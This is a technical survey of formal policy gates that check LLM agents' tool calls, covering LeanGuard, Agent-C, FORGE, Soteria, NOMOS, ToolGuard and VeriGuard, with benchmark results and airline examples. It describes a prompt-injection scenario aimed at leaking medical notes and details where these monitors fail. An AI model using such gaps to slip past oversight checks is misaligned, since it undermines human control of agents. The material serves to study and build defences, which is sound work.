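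LeanGuard allows a call only if every relevant part of the policy evaluates without error, which is stricter than testing whether the policy entails permission. For a three-hour-old booking with an unknown flight status, the airline's rule entails permission, but LeanGuard would apparently refuse the call.

For a worked example, suppose the customer who booked K7QX2M also has a second reservation, H4LN9P, which she booked three hours ago. The log contains five events:

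1. The agent looks up K7QX2M.
2. The agent looks up H4LN9P.
3. The customer confirms that she wants to cancel H4LN9P.
4. The agent looks up H4LN9P again.
5. The agent proposes to cancel H4LN9P.

A simple policy, with its temporal rules scoped to the reservation in the call, gives this result:

| Rule | Condition | Value at event 5 |
|---|---|---|
| Permit | `cancel_reservation` is one of the agent's tools | True |
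| Requirement | ONCE looked up | True, from events 2 and 4 |
| Requirement | SINCE unchanged, confirmed | True: she confirmed at event 3, and nothing has changed the booking since |
| Requirement | Booked within 24 hours, or the airline has cancelled the flight | True: the booking is three hours old |
| Forbid | ONCE cancellation sent | False |
| Errors | A fact is missing or malformed | None |

The gate allows the call. It would have blocked the call if the rule had been "PREVIOUS confirmed" instead of the SINCE rule, because the harmless lookup at event 4 comes between the confirmation and the call. A proposed call to cancel K7QX2M at event 5 would have passed the lookup rule but failed the other two requirements.

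Suppose the airline's system never replies. LeanGuard logs a call as sent before it runs the tool, and keeps that entry while the outcome is unknown. When the agent tries again, "ONCE cancellation sent" is true and the gate blocks the call. If the first call never arrived, the ticket remains uncancelled until someone investigates. For refunds, never sending the request twice is probably worth that delay.

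### What the Lean theorem proves

The evaluator that computes these decisions could have bugs, so Sankar and colleagues defined the policy language's meaning separately, using LeanLTL, a Lean library for *linear temporal logic*. Formulas in this logic usually describe the future, so the definition reverses the log to put the newest event first. Each step forward then goes back in time, so ONCE becomes "eventually" and SINCE becomes "until".

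They then proved that, for every formula and every history, the evaluator returns true exactly when the formula holds under this definition. They also proved that if LeanGuard allows a call, then some permit holds, every requirement holds, no forbid applies and no error occurred. Lean checks the proofs when the developer builds the policy, so they add no time to each call.

The theorem is about the evaluator, so it would hold just as well for a policy with the wrong time limit.

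### Violations with and without LeanGuard

When Sankar and colleagues ran the five Qwen models without a gate, the models made forbidden calls that changed a record in 28 of the 1,390 episodes (2.0%), at least 33 calls in all. With the gate, no forbidden call ran. This follows from the design, because the same rules decide which calls may run and which count as violations.

Violations occurred in 1.6% of episodes with ToolSafe, which uses a trained guard model, and in 2.6% with Progent, whose rules constrain individual calls. Neither rate differs significantly from the rate with no guard. Under Progent, 23 of the 41 forbidden calls that ran broke a temporal rule, as one would expect from a guard that checks one call at a time.

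LeanGuard did less well when a language model judged episodes against the written policy. The judge flagged violations in 9.7% of episodes without the gate, 5.6% when the gate refused calls without giving a reason, and 6.5% when it explained its refusals. With unexplained refusals, the judge flagged 85 calls that the gate had allowed. In 48 of these, its finding about a customer's consent or a fact the gate had checked differed from the gate's. Another 35 involved matters that the formal rules did not cover, such as when to transfer a customer to a human. The judge was also the largest of the five models tested, so some of the episodes it graded were its own.

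Task success fell from 72.7% to 68.9% when calls were refused without explanation. Nearly all the loss was in retail, where success fell by 8.6 points. One retail rule lets the agent modify each order only once, which is stricter than the benchmark's policy. This rule stopped 158 calls and may account for part of the loss. Explaining the refusals recovered some of the lost success.

### Agent-C: checking while the model writes

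LeanGuard waits for a complete call from the host. Agent-C, the system that Kamath and colleagues built, ties the check to the model's generation of the call. Its rules can refer to future calls as well as past ones:

```
Before(cancel_reservation(reservation_id = r1), True,
       get_reservation_details(reservation_id = r2), r1 == r2)

After(write_file(path = p1), True,
      read_file(path = p2), p1 == p2)
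```

The first rule requires a lookup of the same reservation before every cancellation. The second requires a read of the same file after every write. `True` means the rule applies whatever the arguments are. A third form, `Seq`, requires two calls to occur in a given order at some point in the session.

With an open model, Agent-C works like this:

1. The model generates a tool name and then its arguments. Agent-C checks each argument's type as soon as it is complete.
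2. Once the model has supplied all the arguments, Agent-C reads any facts that the rules mention from the tools' own data.
3. It adds the proposed call to the log and asks Z3 whether *some continuation* of that log would satisfy all the rules.
4. If the answer is SAT, the call runs. Otherwise Agent-C discards the tokens back to the tool name, and the model generates another call, with a penalty against repeating the rejected one.
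5. After a fixed number of failures, Agent-C puts an error message into the model's context instead of a call.

With a closed model, Agent-C discards the whole call and prompts the model again.

A satisfiability test is appropriate for Agent-C, though not for Winston and colleagues' gate, because Agent-C gets its facts from the tools and only the agent's future calls are unknown. The test also matches the definition of safety, since Agent-C refuses a call only when no continuation could satisfy the rules.

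Agent-C can detect that a call required by an `After` rule is missing, but it doesn't make the model issue that call. Right after a write, the solver returns SAT because a read could still follow. When the model tries to end the session, Agent-C adds an end marker to the log and runs the solver again. If the file is still unread, the solver returns UNSAT and the session ends with an error status, so the developer learns that the read is missing. The soundness theorems of Kamath and colleagues cover every call that Agent-C lets through and every session that ends normally, but not sessions that end with an error.

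Kamath and colleagues compared Agent-C with agents that had no gate and, for open models, with *AgentSpec*, an earlier rule-based monitor. Each AgentSpec rule specifies a triggering event, conditions to test, and an action, such as blocking the call. In the table, *conformance* is the share of tasks with no policy violation, and *success* is the share that the agent completed without a violation. Agent-C's conformance was 100% in every row.

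| Model and domain | Conformance, no gate | Conformance, AgentSpec | Success, no gate | Success, AgentSpec | Success, Agent-C |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-32B, retail | 37.7% | 84.1% | 25.5% | 37.4% | 53.3% |
| Qwen3-32B, airline | 35.3% | 79.3% | 17.3% | 38.7% | 35.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5, retail | 93.0% | – | 76.5% | – | 80.5% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5, airline | 70.0% | – | 42.0% | – | 43.5% |
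| GPT-5, retail | 91.9% | – | 71.0% | – | 73.6% |
| GPT-5, airline | 71.3% | – | 38.0% | – | 42.8% |

AgentSpec also applies fixed rules but falls far short of 100%, probably more because of the limits of its rule language than because of errors in applying the rules. Kamath and colleagues explain that monitors of this kind can't express conditions on the tools' data, such as who owns an order.

A task completed with a violation counts as a failure, which favors gates. Some of Agent-C's gains may therefore come from completing the same tasks without the violation. Still, the gate raised the two closed models' airline conformance by about 30 points without making them less useful.

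The team also wrote 17 tasks per domain in which the customer wants something forbidden. Sonnet did what the customer wanted in 5 of the 17 retail tasks (29.4%) without a gate and in none with Agent-C.

Backtracking also helped a little. Qwen3-8B succeeded on 42.1% of retail tasks with backtracking and 36.5% with re-prompting.

### FORGE: dependencies instead of order

A log records the order of events, but not whether an earlier event influenced a later one. Suppose the airline runs several agents at once, and one reads a passenger's medical notes, then another emails a hotel about something unrelated. The rule "no outside email after reading medical notes", applied to their shared log, would block the harmless email.

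*Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues, 2026) describes a gate called FORGE (originally PCAS), which keeps a graph of events. An arrow from one event to another means the first may have influenced the second. FORGE draws an arrow from each of an agent's events to its next, from a message to whatever its recipient does next, and from a tool call to its result.

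The policies are in Datalog, a logic language that originated in database research. A Datalog rule has a conclusion on the left and its conditions on the right. Here is a policy for the airline, adapted from Palumbo and colleagues:

```
Tainted(x) :- Untrusted(x).
Tainted(x) :- DependsOn(x, y), Tainted(y).
Secret(x)  :- Private(x).
Secret(x)  :- DependsOn(x, y), Secret(y).
Deny(x)    :- OutsideEmail(x), Tainted(x), Secret(x).
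```

The second and fourth rules are recursive, so they follow influence through any number of steps. Suppose a hotel sends a message (*m*) with planted instructions. An agent reads it along with a passenger's medical notes (*n*) and writes a summary (*s*). A second agent then tries to email the hotel (*e*) after reading the summary. FORGE reasons as follows:

1. *m* is untrusted, so it is tainted. *n* is private, so it is secret.
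2. *s* depends on both, so it is tainted and secret.
3. *e* depends on *s*, so it is tainted and secret too.
4. *e* is an outside email, so FORGE derives `Deny(e)` and blocks it.

The second agent never saw the hotel's message or the notes, so a check on its own history would have missed the connection.

If FORGE derives both `Allow` and `Deny`, `Deny` takes precedence, as in Cedar. If it derives neither, the developer's chosen default applies. Evaluation always terminates with a single answer because the set of facts is finite.

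Datalog treats anything it can't derive as false. This is safe for a rule like "deny a protected call that has no approval", since a missing approval leads to a refusal. But it is dangerous for the email policy. If the host fails to mark the hotel's message as untrusted, FORGE can't derive `Tainted(e)`, and the email goes out unless another rule or the default stops it. LeanGuard's error condition is meant to catch missing data, although it too would miss an incorrect label.

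The graph also helps less with a single agent. Nobody can see which parts of a model's context influenced its output, so everything the agent has read counts as an influence on everything it does afterwards. Once the agent has read both the hotel's message and the notes, this policy blocks all its outside emails.

Palumbo and colleagues report that on AgentDojo, FORGE was about as secure as information-flow control and let the agents complete substantially more tasks.

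### Soteria: verifying the plan first

All these gates can let an agent start a task that the rules won't allow it to finish. For example, it might cancel a customer's old flight before a gate blocks the replacement booking. Soteria, the system from He and colleagues, has the model write a plan and verifies it before any tool runs.

The plan is a *guarded transition system*, a kind of flowchart. Its nodes are *states*, which represent stages of the task. Its arrows are *transitions*, each of which can call one tool. A transition can have a *guard*, a condition on the data collected so far, and the agent can take that transition only if the guard is true. In this example, a model has written a plan for cancelling a reservation:

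| State | Tool call | Next state |
|---|---|---|
| Look up | Get the reservation | Compute age |
| Compute age | Compute the hours since booking | Decide |
| Decide | None | Cancel if hours ≤ 24, otherwise Deny |
| Cancel | Cancel the reservation | Done |
| Done | None | End, with the task complete |
| Deny | None | End, with the reservation unchanged |

The airline in this example has two rules. The agent may cancel a trip only within 24 hours of booking, and it must first check that the customer hasn't already flown any part of it. The plan follows the first rule but omits the check that the second requires.

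Each tool has a *contract*, with a precondition on its inputs and a postcondition on its result. Soteria works through the plan and records what must be true on reaching each state *s*. Call this $\Sigma(s)$. It then uses Dafny, a program verifier that relies on an SMT solver, to check three conditions:

**Tool contracts.** Whenever the plan calls a tool, the facts known at that point must guarantee the tool's precondition. If *g* is the guard and $P_a$ is the precondition of tool *a*, then $\Sigma(s) \land g \Rightarrow P_a$ must hold.

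The **progress** check requires that the plan not get stuck. Some possible run must reach each state, and in each state with guards $g_1, \dots, g_m$ at least one guard must be true, so $\Sigma(s) \Rightarrow (g_1 \lor \dots \lor g_m)$. If the model had written the guards "hours < 24" and "hours > 24", a booking exactly 24 hours old would match neither, and the check would fail.

**Policy compliance.** Every path to an end state has to satisfy every policy rule. To check this, Soteria adds an imaginary log to the plan, which records each call's position, inputs and result. The rule about flown flights becomes

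$$\forall c \in \text{Cancel}\;\; \exists d \in \text{NotFlown}:\; d \prec c \,\land\, d.\text{id} = c.\text{id} \,\land\, d.\text{result} = \text{true},$$

where $d \prec c$ means that *d* came before *c*.

The faulty plan passes the first two checks and fails the third. On the path to "Done", the log contains a cancellation and no flown-status check, so no *d* exists. The path to "Deny" passes because it contains no cancellation. Dafny reports the error, and Soteria sends the model a message that names the broken rule. The model can then add a state that checks the flown status and leads to "Deny" if the customer has already flown.

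The same method handles the rule "read a file back after writing it", because every path through the plan is finite and Dafny can check that each one includes the read. Soteria rejects plans with loops, which would allow endless paths. To keep plans short, it lets the model reuse verified *sub-plans*, such as one for cancellations, and relies only on their contracts.

Verification assumes that tools behave as their contracts describe and that the agent follows the plan, but the agent is a language model and may do something else. Soteria can restrict the agent to the calls in the plan, though its normal mode shows the agent the remaining steps and lets it choose. A monitor therefore checks every call against the policy rules and the log, and blocks any call that would break a rule. This works even if the plan never passed verification. When the session ends, the monitor also checks for required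 steps that never happened.

The rule about flown flights relies on an earlier tool result, which can become outdated. If the customer takes two hours to confirm and her plane leaves before she does, the old "not flown" result still satisfies the formula. LeanGuard avoids this problem by reading the current record for each decision.

### Soteria's results

He and colleagues tested Soteria on 207 tasks: 50 airline and 114 retail tasks from *τ²-Bench*, and 43 from Toolathlon, a benchmark of long tasks with files and other office tools. With all four models, Soteria had 100% conformance and no violations. Without a gate, conformance was between 58% and 82% on airline tasks, 86% and 90% on retail, and 42% and 56% on Toolathlon. The next table gives the share of tasks completed without a violation:

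| Model | Airline, no gate | Airline, Soteria | Retail, no gate | Retail, Soteria | Toolathlon, no gate | Toolathlon, Soteria |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.4-mini | 34.0% | 60.0% | 20.2% | 35.1% | 2.3% | 11.6% |
| Gemini 3 Flash | 28.0% | 62.0% | 34.2% | 45.6% | 2.3% | 16.3% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 30.0% | 70.0% | 31.6% | 56.1% | 4.7% | 9.3% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 52.0% | 88.0% | 46.5% | 90.4% | 11.6% | 18.6% |

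The 100% is measured against the formal rules, which can be looser than the policy. One rule lets any insured customer cancel, but an example plan in the same paper also requires a health or weather reason.

The gains in success are large, but the agents without a gate did surprisingly badly. Opus 4.6 scored 46.5% in retail, while Kamath et al. got 76.5% from the older Sonnet 4.5 on an earlier version of those tasks. He et al. set reasoning effort to low and had each model play its own customer, which may explain some of the difference. Opus often collected the information it needed and then handed the customer to a human instead of making the change. A plan that names the next step helps a lot with that problem, but a better-configured agent might not have the problem in the first place.

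The ablation on airline tasks adds one component at a time:

| Configuration | GPT-5.4-mini, conformance | GPT-5.4-mini, success | Gemini 3 Flash, conformance | Gemini 3 Flash, success |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Unverified plan | 74% | 44% | 54% | 32% |
| + verification | 80% | 46% | 56% | 32% |
| + sub-plans | 80% | 50% | 58% | 38% |
| + monitor | 100% | 60% | 100% | 62% |

Most of the improvement came from the monitor. Verification alone removed few violations, presumably because the agents didn't stick to their verified plans. Adding the monitor stopped Gemini from breaking rules without reducing the share of tasks it completed, which stayed at 62% when tasks completed with violations are included. The results table has no row for the monitor without a plan, so it doesn't show how much the planning contributes.

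AgentSpec is the nearest substitute for that row. In five runs with GPT-5.4-mini, it averaged 48.0% success on airline tasks. Soteria averaged 50.8%, with fewer planning attempts than in the main test. The confidence intervals overlap, so verified plans may have only a small advantage over a simple monitor for this model.

All success rates on Toolathlon are low. Soteria's 9.3% to 18.6% is 4 to 8 of the 43 tasks. If violations are ignored, Opus completed 13 tasks without a gate and 8 with Soteria, and Haiku completed 7 without a gate and 4 with Soteria. Whether that drop is a real loss depends on how much the broken rules matter. The most common violations were writing a file without first looking at what was there and not reading it back afterwards, and a file can be correct without either check.

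The read-back rule is also the one rule for which Soteria's "hard conformance guarantee" is overstated. The agents read their files back in these tests because the plan and the displayed remaining steps called for it. If an agent had stopped right after a write, the monitor could only have reported the missing read.

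## Turning a written policy into formal rules

The proof behind LeanGuard covers its evaluator, and Soteria's verification covers the agent's plan. Both assume that the formal rules are correct. But a person or a model wrote those rules from a document in ordinary English and may have misread it, so a correct checker can still enforce the wrong policy.

### Four kinds of defect

Suppose the airline extends its policy. The agent must verify a customer's identity, with a tool called `verify_customer`, before doing anything else. It must get her confirmation before cancelling, and it may not cancel a trip once she has flown any part of it. A translation into logic could go wrong in four ways:

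| Defect | Airline example | What happens |
|---|---|---|
| Invalid syntax or types | A rule compares the booking date, stored as text, with the number 24 | The solver or compiler reports an error |
| Omitted clause | No rule mentions flights already flown | A customer flies to Boston, then cancels the whole round trip |
| Rule too weak | The confirmation rule accepts any earlier "yes" | A customer who agreed to a seat change has "confirmed" a cancellation |
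| Rule blocks what it depends on | No tool may run before verification, including `verify_customer` | The gate refuses every call |

A developer will notice a type error or a blocked `verify_customer` call almost immediately, because nothing works. Omitted clauses and weak rules are harder to spot, because the agent still serves ordinary customers normally and the mistake shows only when the gate allows a call it should have refused.

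### Winston's four translation designs

Winston and colleagues tried four ways of translating *τ²-Bench*'s airline policy for their solver gate:

1. **Direct generation.** A model wrote the SMT-LIB code in one attempt. The code had syntax errors, undefined symbols and incomplete rules.
2. **Generation with repair.** Z3's error messages went back to the model, which corrected its code. The result was valid, but it had only 50 to 60 lines and omitted many essential constraints.
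3. **A commercial formalizer.** The Automated Reasoning tool in Amazon Bedrock produced about 600 lines. A language model acting as judge put its coverage of the policy at around 95%. Many rules were too weak, including the one-way rule that allowed cancellation within 24 hours without forbidding it later.
4. **The same tool with custom instructions and manual tuning.** The team defined missing variables, converted timestamps, simplified declarations and tightened weak rules. They used this version in their experiments.

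The repair loop could fix only the problems Z3 reported, and a missing rule doesn't cause Z3 to report one. The coverage score could also miss problems, since a clause can be present in the encoding and still be too weak.

Winston and colleagues found some of the weak rules by running the benchmark and looking at what went wrong, then evaluated the gate on the same benchmark. The share of invalid write calls would probably be higher than the 29% they measured for a newly translated policy that had not been tuned this way.

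Amazon has since added workflows to help with the tuning. According to AWS's *Automated Reasoning checks in Amazon Bedrock Guardrails add new policy refinement workflows* (2026), one revises a policy until it passes tests that the customer has written, and another rewrites variable descriptions that often lead to ambiguous translations. The first could repair the one-way cancellation rule if the customer had written a test for a booking more than 24 hours old.

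### NOMOS: a smaller language for the model

Yu and colleagues' compiler, NOMOS, gives the model much less freedom. A rule consists of a type, a condition, the tools it applies to and the policy sentence it came from. The type is either *forbidden*, which blocks a call while the condition is true, or *precondition*, which blocks a call until the condition is true. The model has to pick the condition from a fixed list, which has 34 entries across the three *τ²-Bench* domains. A person writes the list in advance, along with the code that evaluates each entry.

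The compiler has four passes:

1. *Parse* splits the policy into clauses and records which section each came from.
2. *Extract* asks a language model to turn each clause into candidate rules of the form "block these tools when this condition holds". It does this five times, because the model's output varies. Ordinary code then works out the rule's type from the condition. In an earlier version with free-form output, some rules came out inverted and blocked exactly the calls that the policy permitted.
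3. *Resolve* repairs or rejects defective candidates, merges duplicates and drops rules that too few of the five samples contain.
4. *Materialize* writes out the surviving rules and a report of every repair and rejection.

Only the second pass uses a model, an openly released one with 26 billion parameters.

The checks in the third pass need no solver or model, only the tools' schemas and two tables. For each condition *π*, the table Enable(*π*) lists the tools that can satisfy a rule with that condition, so that it stops blocking. Reads(*π*) lists the arguments that the condition inspects. If *T* is the set of tools that a rule guards and $P_t$ is the set of arguments of tool *t*, the main repair is

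$$T' = T \setminus \text{Enable}(\pi) \setminus \{\,t : \text{Reads}(\pi) \neq \emptyset \,\land\, \text{Reads}(\pi) \cap P_t = \emptyset \,\}.$$

The first subtraction removes the tools that the rule depends on. The second removes tools that take none of the arguments the condition reads, because the rule could never work on them. If no tools are left, the compiler rejects the rule.

The retail policy tells the agent to identify the customer at the start of the conversation, by email address or by name and zip code. The model turned this into a rule that blocked all tools until the agent had done so. But the agent can identify a customer only by calling `find_user_id_by_email` or, if she gives her name and zip code, `find_user_id_by_name_zip`, and the rule blocked these too. Both are in Enable(*π*), so the compiler removes them from the guarded set. The repaired rule blocks the other tools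 until one of these two has succeeded.

The next table shows what happened to all the candidates. A repaired candidate stays in the pool, so it also appears in one of the lower rows.

| Outcome | Airline | Retail |
|---|---|---|
| Candidates from five samples | 79 | 53 |
| Repaired: blocked the tools it depends on | 0 | 4 |
| Repaired: required confirmation for read-only tools | 5 | 0 |
| Read an argument that the tool doesn't have | 8 | 1 |
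| Rejected: no available tool could ever satisfy it | 5 | 0 |
| Rejected: guarded "all tools" and couldn't be narrowed | 11 | 2 |
| **All structural defects** | **29 (36.7%)** | **7 (13.2%)** |
| Rejected: in too few samples | 3 | 1 |
| Merged as duplicates | 42 | 45 |
| **Enforced** | **10** | **5** |

Most of the reduction from 79 rules to ten, and from 53 to five, comes from merging duplicates, because a rule that the model extracts reliably appears once in each of the five samples.

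To find out how much the third-pass checks matter, Yu and colleagues extracted a new set of candidates and compiled it with all of those checks switched off. Eight of the 14 resulting airline rules and three of the five retail rules could never work. With the checks on, no such rules remained, but that result is almost guaranteed because the test for a working rule covers the same faults as the checks.

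Rules written by a stronger model still needed checking. A frontier model produced 91 candidate rules for the airline domain, and six of them read an argument that their tool doesn't have. Another of its rules required authentication for all 14 tools, but the domain has no authentication tool, so the rule would have refused every call.

The check for self-blocking tests each rule separately, so it can miss two rules that block each other. Suppose one rule forbids looking up a reservation before verifying the customer, and another forbids verifying the customer before looking up the reservation. Each rule would pass the check, but together they would stop the agent from doing either.

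### Replaying old conversations

A rule can work mechanically and still have the wrong meaning. NOMOS checks for such rules by replaying recorded conversations in which an agent without a gate succeeded, and counting how many of the agent's calls each rule would have refused. This requires no further model calls.

The clearest error the replay caught was in a trial version of the telecom rules. The policy tells the agent to "always check that the bill is overdue before sending a payment request". The compiled rule instead forbade payment requests while a bill was overdue, which is the only time the agent should send one. In the replay, the rule refused 47 of the 49 payment requests in successful conversations. The same condition guarded the tool that restores a suspended phone line, where it refused none of 44 calls. A developer should therefore remove the rule from the payment tool and keep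 it on the line-restoring tool.

NOMOS flags a rule if the rule refuses at least 90% of a tool's calls in successful conversations. Yu and colleagues chose 90% with this one example in mind, so the threshold may not suit other policies. No airline or retail rule reached 90%. The highest rate was 5 refusals in 6 calls, for `book_reservation`, mostly because the agent had made a second change after a single confirmation.

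The replay also cannot detect missing or weak rules, because it flags only refused calls, and these faults let through calls that should be refused.

### What NOMOS prevented

Yu and colleagues measured violations against separate rules they wrote by hand, 16 for the airline and 11 for retail. Using the compiled rules would have been circular, because the gate enforces those rules and would score perfectly.

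| | Airline, no gate | Airline, NOMOS | Retail, no gate | Retail, NOMOS |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Violations among state-changing calls | 234 of 353 (66.3%) | 3 of 116 (2.6%) | 188 of 611 (30.8%) | 40 of 582 (6.9%) |
| Same, if one "yes" can cover several changes | 36.8% | 2.6% | 13.6% | 5.3% |
| State-changing calls per conversation | 1.41 | 0.46 | 1.34 | 1.28 |
| Violations per conversation | 0.94 | 0.01 | 0.41 | 0.09 |

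The second row concerns the clause on confirmation. Suppose the agent announces two cancellations, the customer says yes once, and the agent carries out both. The stricter reading counts the second cancellation as a violation because her yes covered only the first. The permissive reading accepts both. In retail, more than half of the violations that occur without a gate count as violations only under the stricter reading. NOMOS reduces violations considerably under either reading, but the size of the improvement depends on which one applies, and only the policy's owner can decide that.

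The denominators count only calls that ran. NOMOS blocked another 226 attempts on the airline tasks and 208 in retail. The gated airline agent therefore made only a third as many changes. Its 2.6% rate is based on just 116 calls, so the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from 0.9% to 7.3%. Violations per conversation are a better measure of the total effect, because an agent can't lower that figure by making many harmless calls. In retail, the number of changes barely fell, so less activity can't explain the improvement there.

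Of the 40 remaining retail violations, 21 involved two clauses that the compiler had omitted. One restricts where a refund may go, and the other forbids exchanging an item for itself. The hand-written rules had originally missed these violations too, and Yu and colleagues found them only when auditing a sample of calls. Adding two rules to the set used to measure violations raised the gated agent's measured violation rate from 3.3% to 6.9%, although its behavior had not changed.

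The audit used Claude Sonnet 4.5 as a second judge, which agreed with the hand-written rules on only about half of 160 sampled calls. Of the 77 disagreements over the encoded clauses, only three were violations that the rules had missed. Another 43 were about how to interpret the confirmation clause. In 30 more, the transcript showed that Claude was wrong. For example, it ruled that four bookings made 23 hours earlier were too old for the 24-hour window.

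Some policy clauses were in neither set of rules, so the measured rates don't cover them. When Claude saw the full policy, it flagged 14 calls that the hand-written rules had passed, for problems such as a changed destination or a cancellation reason that the insurance doesn't cover.

### Code tested on generated examples

Zwerdling, Boaz and colleagues (2025), in *Towards Enforcing Company Policy Adherence in Agentic Workflows*, compile a policy into ordinary Python code. Their system, ToolGuard, works in three steps:

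1. A language model finds the passages of the policy that apply to each tool. It also writes examples of permitted and forbidden requests.
2. The system turns the examples into tests.
3. A model writes a guard function for each tool. A type checker and the tests report errors, and the model revises the code until every test passes or it runs out of attempts.

Zwerdling and colleagues measured the first step on the airline policy, using a mapping they had made by hand. They found that 88% of the passages GPT-4o selected were relevant, but it found only 77% of the relevant passages. They consider omissions the more serious problem, because an expert can more easily delete an irrelevant passage than notice a missing one. Adding irrelevant airline rules to the document reduced the combined score from 0.80 to 0.67, which suggests that the step would work less well for companies with long policies.

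They also wrote 61 tests by hand. Guards built from the hand-made mapping passed 82% of these on average with the best model, and guards built from GPT-4o's mapping passed 75%, even though the code had already been through the repair loop.

Imperfect guards still helped. On 22 airline tasks in which the customer asks for something forbidden, the fully automatic version raised pass^1 from 0.450 to 0.685 and pass^10 from 0.227 to 0.500. Reminding the agent of the policy before each action raised pass^10 only to 0.273. Because all of these tasks involve a forbidden request, the results don't show how often the guards obstruct customers whose requests are allowed.

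It is unclear whether the guards can enforce the confirmation rule. Zwerdling and colleagues describe guards with access to the conversation history. *PolicyGuard* (2026), which tested ToolGuard's public code, reports that the generated guards receive no chat history and so can't check what the customer agreed to. The released version may differ from the one used in the original experiments. Developers can already use ToolGuard in Langflow, a tool for building agents. Langflow's *Policies (Beta)* describes a component that generates guard code from written rules.

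### Code proved against a contract

Miculicich, Parmar and colleagues (2025), in *VeriGuard*, add a proof. A language model writes a policy function in Python and a separate list of logical constraints. A validation step looks for ambiguities and asks the user to resolve them, or picks the most plausible interpretation if no user is available. After a round of generated tests, a verifier called Nagini tries to prove that the function meets its contract. For the airline's cancellation rule, the contract might be

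$$\{h \ge 0\}\;\; \texttt{policy}(h, c)\;\; \{\text{result} = (h \le 24 \lor c)\},$$

where *h* is the number of hours since booking and *c* means that the airline has cancelled the flight. The notation means that if the condition on the left holds before the function runs, the condition on the right holds afterwards. If the proof fails, Nagini's error goes back to the model for another attempt.

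Suppose the model misreads "within 24 hours of booking" as "at least 24 hours before departure". It could write that condition into both the function and the contract, and the proof would succeed. The gate would then allow K7QX2M, booked 13 days ago, to be cancelled as long as the flight was more than a day away. Miculicich and colleagues acknowledge that the soundness of their verification depends on a person checking that the constraints match what the user meant.

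On Agent Security Bench, a collection of attacks on agents, VeriGuard reduced the attack success rate to zero with all four models tested. Without a defence, the rate was 51.9% with Gemini 2.5 Flash. Asking a language model whether each action complied with the policy also stopped every attack, but the agent then completed only 40.2% of its tasks, compared with 63.3% under VeriGuard. This difference may come more from how VeriGuard responds to a violation than from its verified code, because task completion fell to 38.1% when VeriGuard only blocked the offending action.

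The proof itself seems to have contributed little to these results. When Miculicich and colleagues added the components one by one, attacks fell to zero before they added formal verification.

VeriGuard also made every access decision correctly on a medical database test. On a test of web agents it was right 95% to 97% of the time, and most of its mistakes were refusals of permitted actions.

### Evidence of faithfulness

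These methods provide different kinds of evidence, and most of it concerns something other than the original text. Consider how each would fare with three mistakes in the airline's rules:

| Evidence | `verify_customer` blocks itself | The rule on flown flights is missing | "24 hours" means before departure |
|---|---|---|---|
| NOMOS's structural checks | Finds it | Miss it | Miss it |
| Replay of successful conversations | Finds it | Misses it | Finds it only if the rule refuses most legitimate cancellations |
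| Tests generated from the model's reading | Find it if they cover verification | Miss it if the model overlooked the clause | Miss it if they share the misreading |
| Proof against a generated contract | Misses it if the contract also blocks every tool | Misses it if the contract omits it too | Misses it if the contract shares the misreading |
| Tests that a person writes from the policy | Find it if they cover verification | Find it if they cover a flown flight | Find it if they cover an old booking |

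Only the last row compares the rules with an independent reading of the policy. For the airline, someone who hasn't seen the formal rules should write these tests, with cases on both sides of every limit, such as bookings 23 and 25 hours old. They should also mark every sentence in the policy that has no rule. NOMOS makes this easier by storing the source sentence with each rule. Its compiler extracted candidates from only 6 of the 8 sections in the airline policy and 8 of the 12 in retail. A reader would have to decide whether the other sections contain anything a gate could enforce.

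People also misread policies. NOMOS turned the airline clause "Basic economy flights cannot be modified" into a rule that blocks every call to `update_reservation_flights` for such bookings. But the policy lets these customers change cabin if they keep the same flights, and that change uses the same tool. Yu and colleagues confirmed four false refusals of this kind in a sample. Their hand-written rules contained the same mistake, so 10 of the 234 airline violations they counted were permitted cabin changes. In a replay, the hand-written rules agreed with all 228 refusals made by the compiled airline rules, but this agreement did not show that either set was correct.

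### Rules that no policy document contains

Even a perfect translation of a policy covers only what its writers thought of. Doshi and colleagues propose finding additional rules with System-Theoretic Process Analysis, a method engineers use to look for hazards in aircraft and autonomous vehicles. It focuses on how components interact, because accidents can happen even when every component works as designed.

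For the calendar agent that revealed a medical appointment to its user's coworkers, the analysis goes like this:

1. List the people whom the agent affects. These are the user and the other people invited to her meetings.
2. List what they value, and turn each value into a possible loss. The user values privacy and could lose it. The others value timely notice and could hear about a change too late.
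3. Identify behavior that could cause each loss, such as an email that includes private information.
4. Decide which losses are serious enough to prevent, and write requirements. Emails must omit private reasons unless the user authorizes them, and the agent must notify everyone promptly.
5. Turn the requirements into rules about data and tool calls. No email may contain data that is private from its recipient, and an email to every attendee must directly follow each change to an event.

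The airline could use the same method. Suppose two colleagues share a reservation and one asks the agent to cancel it. Under the policy, cancellation depends only on the booking time and the flight's status, so the gate allows the call, and the other passenger arrives at the airport without a ticket. An analysis that listed her among the people affected could lead to a new rule that every adult on a reservation must confirm a cancellation. A compiler could not have extracted this rule because it isn't in the policy.

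Doshi and colleagues sort the resulting rules into four groups: flows to block, to require, to allow without asking, and to allow only if the user confirms. The last group is meant to be small, because people who get too many approval requests stop reading them.

Doshi and colleagues tested the approach on a model of the calendar agent in Alloy, a language for describing systems in logic. Alloy's analyzer searches every possible sequence of steps up to a chosen length. It quickly found sequences that leaked private data when the model had no rules, but found none once the rules were added. The agent could still reschedule a meeting and email the participants under the rules. The search could have missed leaks that need a longer sequence, and the researchers have not yet tried the rules on a running agent.

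## Which facts the gate trusts and what its guarantee covers

Suppose the airline has translated its policy perfectly. The guarantee it wants from a gate is the conclusion of an argument, and the translation secures only the first premise:

1. The formal rules are right.
2. The facts that the gate reads are true.
3. Every consequential call passes through the gate.
4. Each tool does what its description says.
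5. Therefore no forbidden call runs.

LeanGuard adds a theorem that the evaluator applies the rules correctly. Sankar and colleagues state that the wider guarantee also requires the facts to be true and the gate to check every call. Palumbo and colleagues state the same two conditions for FORGE.

### Three sources of facts

In Winston and colleagues' gate, GPT-4o reads the conversation and fills in the policy's variables. LeanGuard's host takes a snapshot of the database before each decision and combines it with the log of earlier calls. NOMOS updates its store of facts only from fields in real tool results and the user's messages, so the agent's claims never enter it.

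| Gate | Where a fact comes from | What could make it false |
|---|---|---|
| Winston and colleagues | A language model's reading of the conversation | A misreading, or a false statement by the customer, the agent or an attacker |
| LeanGuard | A database snapshot and the gate's own log | A wrong record, or a bug in the code that reads it |
| NOMOS | Fields in tool results, and the user's messages | A wrong record, or a message that the gate misinterprets |

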